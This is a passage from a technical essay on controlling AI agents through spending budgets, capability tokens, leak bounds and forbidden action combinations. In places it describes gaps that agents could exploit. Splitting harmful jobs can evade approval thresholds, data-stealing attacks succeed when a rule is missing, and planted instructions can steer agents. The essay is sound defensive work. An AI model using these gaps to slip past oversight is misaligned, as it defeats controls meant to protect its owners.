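A weighted sum lets low values offset a high one. Suppose the three weights are equal and the threshold is 0.5. Deleting a small backup might score 1 for irreversibility, 0.2 for blast radius and 0.1 for sensitivity, so *I* is about 0.43 and nobody has to approve the deletion, although it is permanent. Using the largest factor instead of the average would catch it, but would also send many more actions for approval. The separate ceilings help because they apply to running totals for the session, so an agent can't avoid them by splitting a harmful job into small steps.

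No way of adding separate scores is reliable when the harm comes from a combination. The firm's two staff lists might each deserve a low score, but together they reveal what everyone earns. Muruaga's system also lists forbidden combinations of actions, such as reading confidential data and then sending an external message. In one benchmark, none of 544 data-stealing attacks succeeded with the full list, but 39.9% did when one pair was missing. Muruaga credits the blocked attacks in the main tests to the forbidden combinations, approvals and checks against the declared task, so those tests provide little evidence about how well the numeric ceilings work.

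Adding risks gives a safe upper bound on both the expected loss and the chance of any loss, even when the risks are correlated. Suppose that each of 40 payments of €200 has a 1% chance of going to a fraudster. The expected loss is 40 × 1% × €200 = €80, whether or not the risks are independent. The chance that at least one payment goes to a fraudster is 33% if the risks are independent, and at most 40 × 1% = 40% if they are not.

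Unlike the expected loss, the chance of losing everything depends on whether the failures are independent. If they are, the chance that all 40 payments go wrong is 1 in 10⁸⁰. If the same wording would deceive the model on every invoice, it could be as high as 1%. The competition run by Dziemian, Lin and colleagues showed that attacks do carry over in this way. A budget for expected loss would treat the two cases alike. A limit on the number of euros holds in both cases, so it is a better basis for a guarantee than an estimate of risk.

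### Amounts in capture sets

Capture sets and use counts share a structure. *Tracking Captured Variables in Types* (2021), an early paper on capture sets, compares them to coeffects because both describe what code requires from its context. A capture set in effect gives each capability one of two grades, "unlimited" if it is in the set and "none" if it is not.

Scala could add capture sets to `map` without changing its signature partly because unlimited use plus unlimited use is still unlimited use, so it doesn't matter how often `map` calls the function it receives. With numeric amounts, one use plus one use makes two, so the compiler needs the number of calls `map` makes. Numeric amounts would probably require changes to many more function signatures than capture sets did.

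The closest existing combination tracks how code uses a capability, but not how much. Xu, Bračevac and colleagues (2026), in *System Capybara*, extend Scala's capture checking so that a capture set can distinguish reading from writing. A function can also "consume" a capability, after which the compiler rejects any further use of it, including through other functions that hold it. The firm could use this to prevent double payments by giving the program a separate payment slip for each invoice:

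```
def pay(consume slip: PaymentSlip^): Receipt

pay(slip17)
pay(slip17)   // error: slip17 was consumed
```

Consumption works like a grade of `0..1`. Xu and colleagues implemented the system in the Scala 3 compiler and proved in Lean that its core is sound. They have not proved that the compiler follows the theory, or measured how many annotations existing code would need.

| Combination | Status |
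|---|---|
| Capture sets that restrict which capabilities, or which kinds | in Scala 3, still experimental |
| Capture sets with reading, writing and one-time use | in Scala 3, with a proof about the core theory |
| Numeric use counts on variables | in Granule, without capture sets |
| Cost bounds with several quantities | in theories of small languages |
| Capture sets with numeric amounts | a proposal |

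There appears to be no published system of the last type. In such a system, a function that uses the bank connection at most once per call might have the type `Invoice ->{bank: 1} Unit`. The rule for comparing capture sets would have to multiply these counts. If a function `record` uses `log` twice per call, then three uses of `record` need six uses of `log`. Functions without annotations could default to "unlimited" so old code would still compile, but a program that passed them a payment function would have no finite bound on how often it used that function.

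The invoice program doesn't need a system this general. Its two loops have known limits, 40 invoices and 12 payments, and it doesn't pass functions to other functions. A harness could require agents to write their payment code in a small language with the same restrictions, and calculate the bound with the three rules for sequences, branches and loops. Such a language would be too limited for most software, but it may be enough for paying the month's bills.

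## Budgets that can be spent, split and lent

A compiler can show in advance that one program will spend at most €2,400. But the firm may have several agents paying bills at once, or one agent that delegates half the invoices to a helper, and their combined spending has to stay within €2,500. The harness then has to pass parts of the budget between programs, as it does with other capabilities.

Budgets need stricter rules than file handles because copying a budget can increase the total amount spent. If the agent gives its helper a copy of its handle for the invoice folder, both can read the same 40 invoices, but if it also copies its €2,500 limit, the two can spend twice what the firm intended, like the sub-agents in the previous section. A designer can prevent this by keeping the amount in a single object and copying only references to it, or by making the amount a value that programs can't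 copy.

### Meters and space banks in KeyKOS

KeyKOS kept each budget of processor time or storage in a single object. As Bomberger, Frantz and colleagues explain in *The KeyKOS Nanokernel Architecture*, every running program holds a capability for a meter, which lets it run for a certain amount of processor time. The kernel starts with one prime meter that covers all future time, and meters can have submeters. Similarly, a department that had bought a megabyte of storage would get a capability for a space bank containing 256 4-kilobyte pages.

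Programs can copy these capabilities freely, but copying one doesn't provide more processor time because both copies refer to the same meter. The time a program uses also counts against every meter higher in the tree. If a meter with 10 seconds left has two submeters of 10 seconds each, the programs using them can run for 10 seconds in total. A program whose meter reaches zero stops without losing its data and can continue once somebody adds time.

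### Purses and mints

A kernel can measure processor time because it controls the processor. Money needs another mechanism, and Miller, Morningstar and Frantz (2000), in *Capability-based Financial Instruments*, built one from ordinary objects. A mint creates purses, and each purse holds a balance. Spritely Institute's *Simple Mint* is a modern version of their example. In simplified form, it works like this:

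```
function makeMint():
    (seal, unseal) = makeSealerPair()
    function makePurse(balance):
        function decrease(amount):
            if amount < 0 or amount > balance: fail("not allowed")
            balance = balance - amount
        object purse:
            getBalance(): return balance
            sprout(): return makePurse(0)
            getDecrease(): return seal(decrease)
            deposit(amount, source):
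                unseal(source.getDecrease())(amount)
                balance = balance + amount
        return purse
    return makePurse
```

`seal` puts a value in a box that only the matching `unseal` can open, and only this mint's purses have access to `unseal`. The harness keeps `makePurse`, which creates money, and gives the agent a purse with €2,500. To give its helper €1,000, the agent sprouts an empty purse and calls `deposit(1000, main)` on it. The transfer has four steps:

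1. The new purse asks the main purse for its `decrease` function and receives it in a sealed box.
2. The new purse opens the box. If the agent had passed a fake purse of its own making, the transfer would fail here, because the agent cannot seal a box for this mint.
3. The new purse calls `decrease(1000)`, which checks that the main purse has enough money and lowers its balance to €1,500.
4. The new purse raises its own balance to €1,000.

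The total is still €2,500. Without the check for negative amounts in `decrease`, the agent could add €500 to its main purse by depositing −€500 from it into an empty purse, then throw that second purse away.

The agent can keep a reference to the new purse after handing it over, and use it to take the money back. The helper therefore cannot rely on the €1,000 until it has moved the money into a purse that only it holds. Nothing may interrupt the transfer between the check and the change of balance, which is easy to ensure on one computer. Traditional examples relied on such local operations for simplicity, but Tallon's *Digital cash in an asynchronous environment* presents a bank whose objects never have to wait for each other's answers.

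### How agents overspend

The 63 incidents in *Token Budgets* come from public reports about 21 software projects between 2023 and 2026. One user reported about $2,150 of unintended spending. Another lost $235 in four days to a loop in a coding agent. The incidents were found by searching for reports of this kind, so they show that overspending recurs across independent projects, but not how common it is.

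The catalogue also includes 47 feature requests, acknowledged gaps and borderline cases. Of all 110 entries, 27 mainly involve agents that kept retrying, 12 involve software with no usable spending limit, and 11 involve agents that delegated work to others. These counts are rough, because two people who sorted the entries by cause agreed only moderately.

Delegation can break a spending limit that works for one agent. Suppose three agents share a counter. Each checks that enough money remains, makes its call and then records the cost. If all three check before any records a cost, each finds the full budget available.

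### Budgets as affine values

*Token Budgets* presents a library that prevents this mistake in Rust. A budget is an affine value, meaning the compiler lets a program use it at most once:

```
let (mine, helpers) = budget.split(1500, 1000)?;
start_helper(helpers);
let (rest, receipt) = mine.spend(200)?;
budget.spend(200)?;      // error: split already used up budget
```

Splitting a budget uses it up and returns two smaller ones. Spending from a budget also uses it up and returns what is left, along with a receipt that the program can later exchange for a refund if the call used less than expected. The program can merge two budgets into one, but it cannot copy a budget. The compiler rejects the last line because `budget` no longer exists. Rust's compiler already makes these checks to keep memory safe, so the library needs no changes to the language.

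An affine value can go unused. If the helper crashes with €300 left, the other agents can't use that €300, but the crash doesn't let anyone overspend. A linear type system would require the program to account for the remainder, a requirement Rust cannot enforce.

The compiler checks only that no code uses the same budget twice. The program itself checks whether a payment of €200 fits into what remains, by subtracting while it runs. Unlike the cost bounds of the previous section, the library therefore cannot reject an over-budget program in advance. The library also protects budgets only within one running program. Once an agent sends a budget to another computer as data, the type system no longer prevents copying, and a shared service has to track the balance.

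### Three agents and one budget

*Token Budgets* tested delegation by having three agents call Claude Haiku 4.5 at the same time. The amounts below are in thousandths of a US cent. Each call cost 23, except in the last row, where a shorter prompt cost 1. Every method except the counter without a lock set aside an estimated 31 before each call.

| How the agents shared the budget | Budget | Calls allowed per run | Spent per run | Runs over budget |
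|---|---|---|---|---|
| Python counter without a lock | 60 | 3 | 69 | 30 of 30 |
| Python counter with a lock | 60 | 1 | 23 | 0 of 30 |
| Rust budget split three ways | 60 | 0 | 0 | 0 of 30 |
| Rust budget split three ways | 100 | 3 | 69 | 0 of 30 |
| Rust counter with a lock | 60 | 1 | 1 | 0 of 30 |

A lock lets only one agent at a time check the counter and reserve money from it. The two locked counters stayed within the budget as reliably as the affine values did. The advantage of the affine version is that a programmer can't forget the lock. All three attempts to write the faulty Python pattern with the library's budgets failed to compile.

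The 30 runs are little more than one observation, because the model's settings made its answers nearly identical. The result also depends on the budget. With a budget of 100, the unlocked counter would also have stayed within the limit, because three calls use only 69. The test shows that the mistake can happen and that the compiler catches it, but not how often it happens in practice.

A harness that splits a budget evenly among many agents can also waste it, because each share may be too small to use. With a budget of 60, each agent got 20, which was less than the 31 estimated for a call, so none of them could make one. The shared counter with a lock allowed one call from the same budget.

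For a single agent, a four-line Python counter using the same estimates worked as well as the Rust library. None of the 21 projects in the catalogue is written in Rust, so their developers could not use the affine version without rewriting their software.

### Costs that nobody knows in advance

The price of a model call is known only after the model answers, so the library has to reserve an upper estimate first. Its default estimates are four to six times the actual cost. A method that adapts to earlier calls lowers the median estimate to about twice the actual cost. Counting the tokens exactly brings it close to the actual cost, but adds about 0.9 to 1.7 seconds to each call.

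High estimates make the program stop early. In a trial with Rig, a Rust agent framework, an agent had 40 tasks and a limit of $0.05. The library allowed 22 calls, which cost $0.0404, and refused the other 18 because the remaining $0.0096 could not cover the estimated cost of another call. All 40 tasks would have cost about $0.073, so the limit prevented overspending, but it left about a fifth of the budget unspent.

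Reasoning models can instead cost more than the estimate, because they produce hidden text before they answer and providers charge for it. This text can be 5 to 50 times as long as the visible answer, and the usual limit on answer length does not cover it. *Token Budgets* excludes these models from its guarantee and recommends relying first on the provider's own limit for reasoning.

The guarantee also assumes that providers report usage correctly. In a simulation where the provider reported half the true cost, 666 of 1,000 sessions exceeded their budget, and the average overrun across all sessions was 13.9%. When the provider reported a fifth of the true cost, every session exceeded its budget, by an average of 138%. Comparing the account with the actual bill after every three calls reduced that average to 23%.

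### L3M: lending budgets down a tree of agents

*L3M* (Eisenach, George and colleagues, 2026) describes a harness from Amazon in which budgets and other capabilities pass from agent to agent. The harness is written in Lean, a programming language and proof checker. When an agent starts, the harness creates a capability for each kind of access in the agent's grant, such as its folders, its branches in the version-control system Git, or a list of web hosts. (L3M calls these capabilities "tokens", but they are unrelated to the tokens of text that models process.) Each kind has its own type, and every function that interacts with the outside world takes the matching capability as an argument, so a tool without a network capability cannot express a web request.

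Agents can also write new tools for themselves. Each tool's type lists the kinds of access it uses, and the harness offers the tool to the agent only if the agent already holds the matching capabilities. For example, the type of a tool that counts unfinished tasks in a folder lists only file reading.

Each agent has a budget that counts calls to a language model. When it starts a child agent, it lends the child part of this budget, and the harness refuses a loan larger than what the parent has left. If a parent with the budget *L* lends *l*₁, …, *lₙ* to its children and keeps *r*, then Eisenach and colleagues prove that

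*l*₁ + … + *lₙ* + *r* ≤ *L*.

A parent with 100 calls could lend 30 to one child and 50 to another, leaving 20. A loan returns to the parent when the child retires, so if the first child has used 10 of its 30 calls by then, the parent should get back 20. The theorem covers only one batch of loans, not their return or any later loans, although its name in the code refers to a "global" budget.

The proofs about other capabilities have similar limits:

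| What the proof establishes | What it leaves open |
|---|---|
| A new child's access never exceeds its parent's | A human can widen the access later |
| The harness creates only capabilities that the agent's grant includes | The build process prevents forgery, without a proof |
| A tool written by an agent directly names only permitted functions | The proof does not cover what those functions do or the loading process as a whole |

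Eisenach and colleagues do not claim a theorem about the whole system. They rely on the Lean compiler, the Linux kernel, Git and a small amount of C code. The seL4 proofs cover much more of the path from specification to running code, but for a much smaller piece of software.

L3M's restrictions made agents less useful in a test on 37 command-line tasks. With three attempts per task, L3M solved 41.7% when agents had a shell and nobody reviewed their commands, and 27.0% when they had only tools whose effects the harness could undo or whose reach was limited by a capability. Claude Code solved 59.5% with the same model and no permission checks. L3M trailed it even with a shell, so part of the gap comes from the harness, which Eisenach and colleagues say they had not tuned. The test did not measure how well the budgets worked.

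### Measuring how much an agent can leak

Budgets could also limit leaks. Eisenach and colleagues propose an account for each kind of information, such as payroll data. It records how many bytes of that kind an agent has read, and how many bytes of any content the agent has sent since. They have not implemented this design.

An agent can't reveal more about the payroll than it has read, and its messages can't carry more information than their own length. For each kind of information *K*, therefore,

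leaked(*K*) ≤ min(read(*K*), sent(*K*)).

Suppose an agent reads 64 secret bytes and then sends two 50-byte messages. It can have leaked at most min(64, 100) = 64 bytes. Adding up a separate limit for each message would give 50 + 50 = 100, which is too high, because if the first message reveals 50 of the secret bytes, the second can reveal only the other 14. The account therefore has to total all the bytes read and all the bytes sent before taking the smaller total.

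Every message counts in full against every kind of information the agent has read, because the harness can't detect which bytes carry a secret. If an agent has read both payroll and customer data, sending 50 bytes uses 50 bytes from the budget for each. The system treats data from an unlabelled channel as non-public.

The bound is most useful when one agent holds the secrets and another has internet access. Suppose the firm wants to choose payroll software based on its confidential salary data. The agent with internet access sends a numbered list of 16 products to the agent with the salary data, which replies with a number from the list. That reply reveals at most log₂ 16 = 4 bits about the salaries, however many files the agent sending it has read. This holds only if the agent with internet access wrote the list without help from the other agent and the timing of the reply reveals nothing.

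But the bound treats all bytes of one kind alike, so, like any limit on bytes, it could still let one short message carry a whole key.

### Reserving effects before a call

Wei and Xiong (2026), in *Access Control for Agentic AI*, extend reservations from the cost of running a model to other effects with an amount, such as payments. Each tool has a signed description of everything a call to it might do. Before an agent makes a call, a shared ledger checks the amount against the task's budget and reserves it in one step that no other agent can interrupt. If *B* is the budget, then at all times

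reserved + spent ≤ *B*.

Suppose two agents share the firm's €2,500, and the first reserves €1,500 for a payment. If the second then requests €1,200, the ledger rejects the request, even though no money has moved yet. The ledger keeps agents on different computers from overspending a shared budget, as the lock did for three agents in one program.

If the bank's reply gets lost, the agent doesn't know whether the payment went through. As in ScopeGate, each payment therefore carries an identifying key that stays the same when the agent retries. If nobody can find out whether the payment went through, the ledger keeps counting the money as spent.

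Wei and Xiong point out that a budget for each task does not limit the total spending of an agent that can start new tasks. With five tasks at €2,500 each, the agent could spend €12,500. They propose a second budget, for the person or organisation on whose behalf the tasks run, that carries over from one task to the next.

The proof is short, and most of the difficulty lies in its assumptions. The ledger must be available, the bank must recognise repeated payments or at least report what happened to each one, and each tool's description must be accurate. If a service charges €300 for a call that its description limits to €200, the ledger's total is wrong. Wei and Xiong have specified this system but not yet measured how it works in practice.

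### Pricing privileges by their power

*Towards Elastic Least Privilege for Agent Planning* (Parkinson, Wang and Mustafa, 2026) proposes charging agents for the access they hold, even if they don't use it. An agent starts with a small set of permissions and can borrow more for a limited time. Each minute of read access to a resource uses 1 unit of the agent's budget, write access 3, and administrative access 9. The budget refills gradually.

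The price rises as an agent gets closer to a forbidden combination. One such rule says that no agent may combine untrusted input, sensitive data and a way to send data out or change something. If *φ* is the share of a forbidden combination that the agent has already had in the session, the price is multiplied by

1 / (1 − *φ*).

Prices are 1.5 times as high for an agent with one of the three elements and 3 times as high for an agent with two. The system refuses to grant the third, whatever the agent's budget. Giving up access doesn't lower the count, because the agent may still have the data it read. Repeated requests also raise the price.

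In one example, a coding agent has to repair a public project. It borrows read access for six minutes to find the fault, at 1.5 units a minute. It then adds write access and holds both for another six minutes, at a combined 14 units a minute, before returning them. The total is 9 + 84 = 93 units. Borrowing both for 20 minutes at the start would have used 240 units. The harness shows the agent these figures so that it can choose the plan that uses fewer units, but nobody has yet tested whether models do so reliably.

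In a second example, an agent follows a planted instruction to collect private code and publish it. The agent borrows read access to eight private projects before its budget runs out and the system withdraws the access. The rule against the forbidden combination stops the agent from publishing the code, with or without a budget. The budget limits only how many projects the agent can read and for how long. Both examples come from a simulation with settings chosen to illustrate the idea, so they are not evidence of how well it would work.

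The budget sets a firm limit on access. With a capacity of 600 units and a refill of 5 a minute, an agent can use at most 600 + 5 × 60 = 900 units in an hour unless its owner approves more. That is enough for write access to five projects for the whole hour at the basic price. The limit holds whether or not prices affect the model's behavior, as long as the agent has no other way to get access and the system can withdraw access without delay.

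### Who sets the prices

| Proposal | What the budget counts | What determines the amount charged |
|---|---|---|
| *Token Budgets* | money spent on model calls | the provider's prices and reported usage |
| Eisenach and colleagues | model calls | every call counts as one |
| Wei and Xiong | payments and other effects with an amount | a description signed by the service's operator or an authorised auditor |
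| Parkinson and colleagues | access held, by the minute | weights chosen by administrators |

Budgeting in money lets somebody check the account against a bill. Counting calls is simpler, but a call that processes a long document may cost far more than one that answers a short question. In Wei and Xiong's design, the company that sells a service may also describe its effects, and the proof assumes that it does so honestly.

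The weights that a budget assigns to permissions don't correspond to anything outside the system. Parkinson and colleagues say that theirs do not estimate losses, and argue that the order matters more than the exact numbers. Platforms such as GitHub already rank their permissions from reading to administration. But a budget also depends on the ratios between weights. With weights of 1 and 9, reading nine private projects uses as much of the budget as administering one, and a firm can't determine from a ranking whether the two are equally risky.

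Attackers can also exploit a price system. A planted instruction could make an agent waste its budget, leaving nothing for its real work. If prices are visible, high ones may show attackers which files are worth stealing. Parkinson and colleagues suggest showing only broad price bands to reveal less.

### When one cheap call does the damage

At these rates, an agent that has read untrusted text uses about 0.05 of its 600 units to hold read access to a private project for one second, which may be long enough to copy a password. Parkinson and colleagues acknowledge that their budget limits exposure, not harm. Where misuse can't be undone, they recommend forbidding access or requiring approval for each use.

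Wei and Xiong sort effects by whether anyone can reverse them. An agent may have standing permission to read data and make changes it can undo, but disclosures and payments need fresh approval from a person. The invoice agent would have to ask the bookkeeper about every bill, or at least every batch, which could bring back approval fatigue.

L3M requires less approval. By default, it reviews a call only if the harness cannot undo its effects and no capability limits its reach. An agent can therefore send data without review to a web host that a person has already approved. This avoids many interruptions, but Eisenach and colleagues acknowledge that approving a destination does not make every disclosure to it acceptable.

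A budget cannot prevent harmful actions that use none of it. An agent that changes a supplier's account number in the firm's register spends no money and sends no data out, yet that one change could divert every later payment meant for that supplier. To prevent this, the firm should give the agent a read-only copy of the register and leave changes to the bookkeeper.
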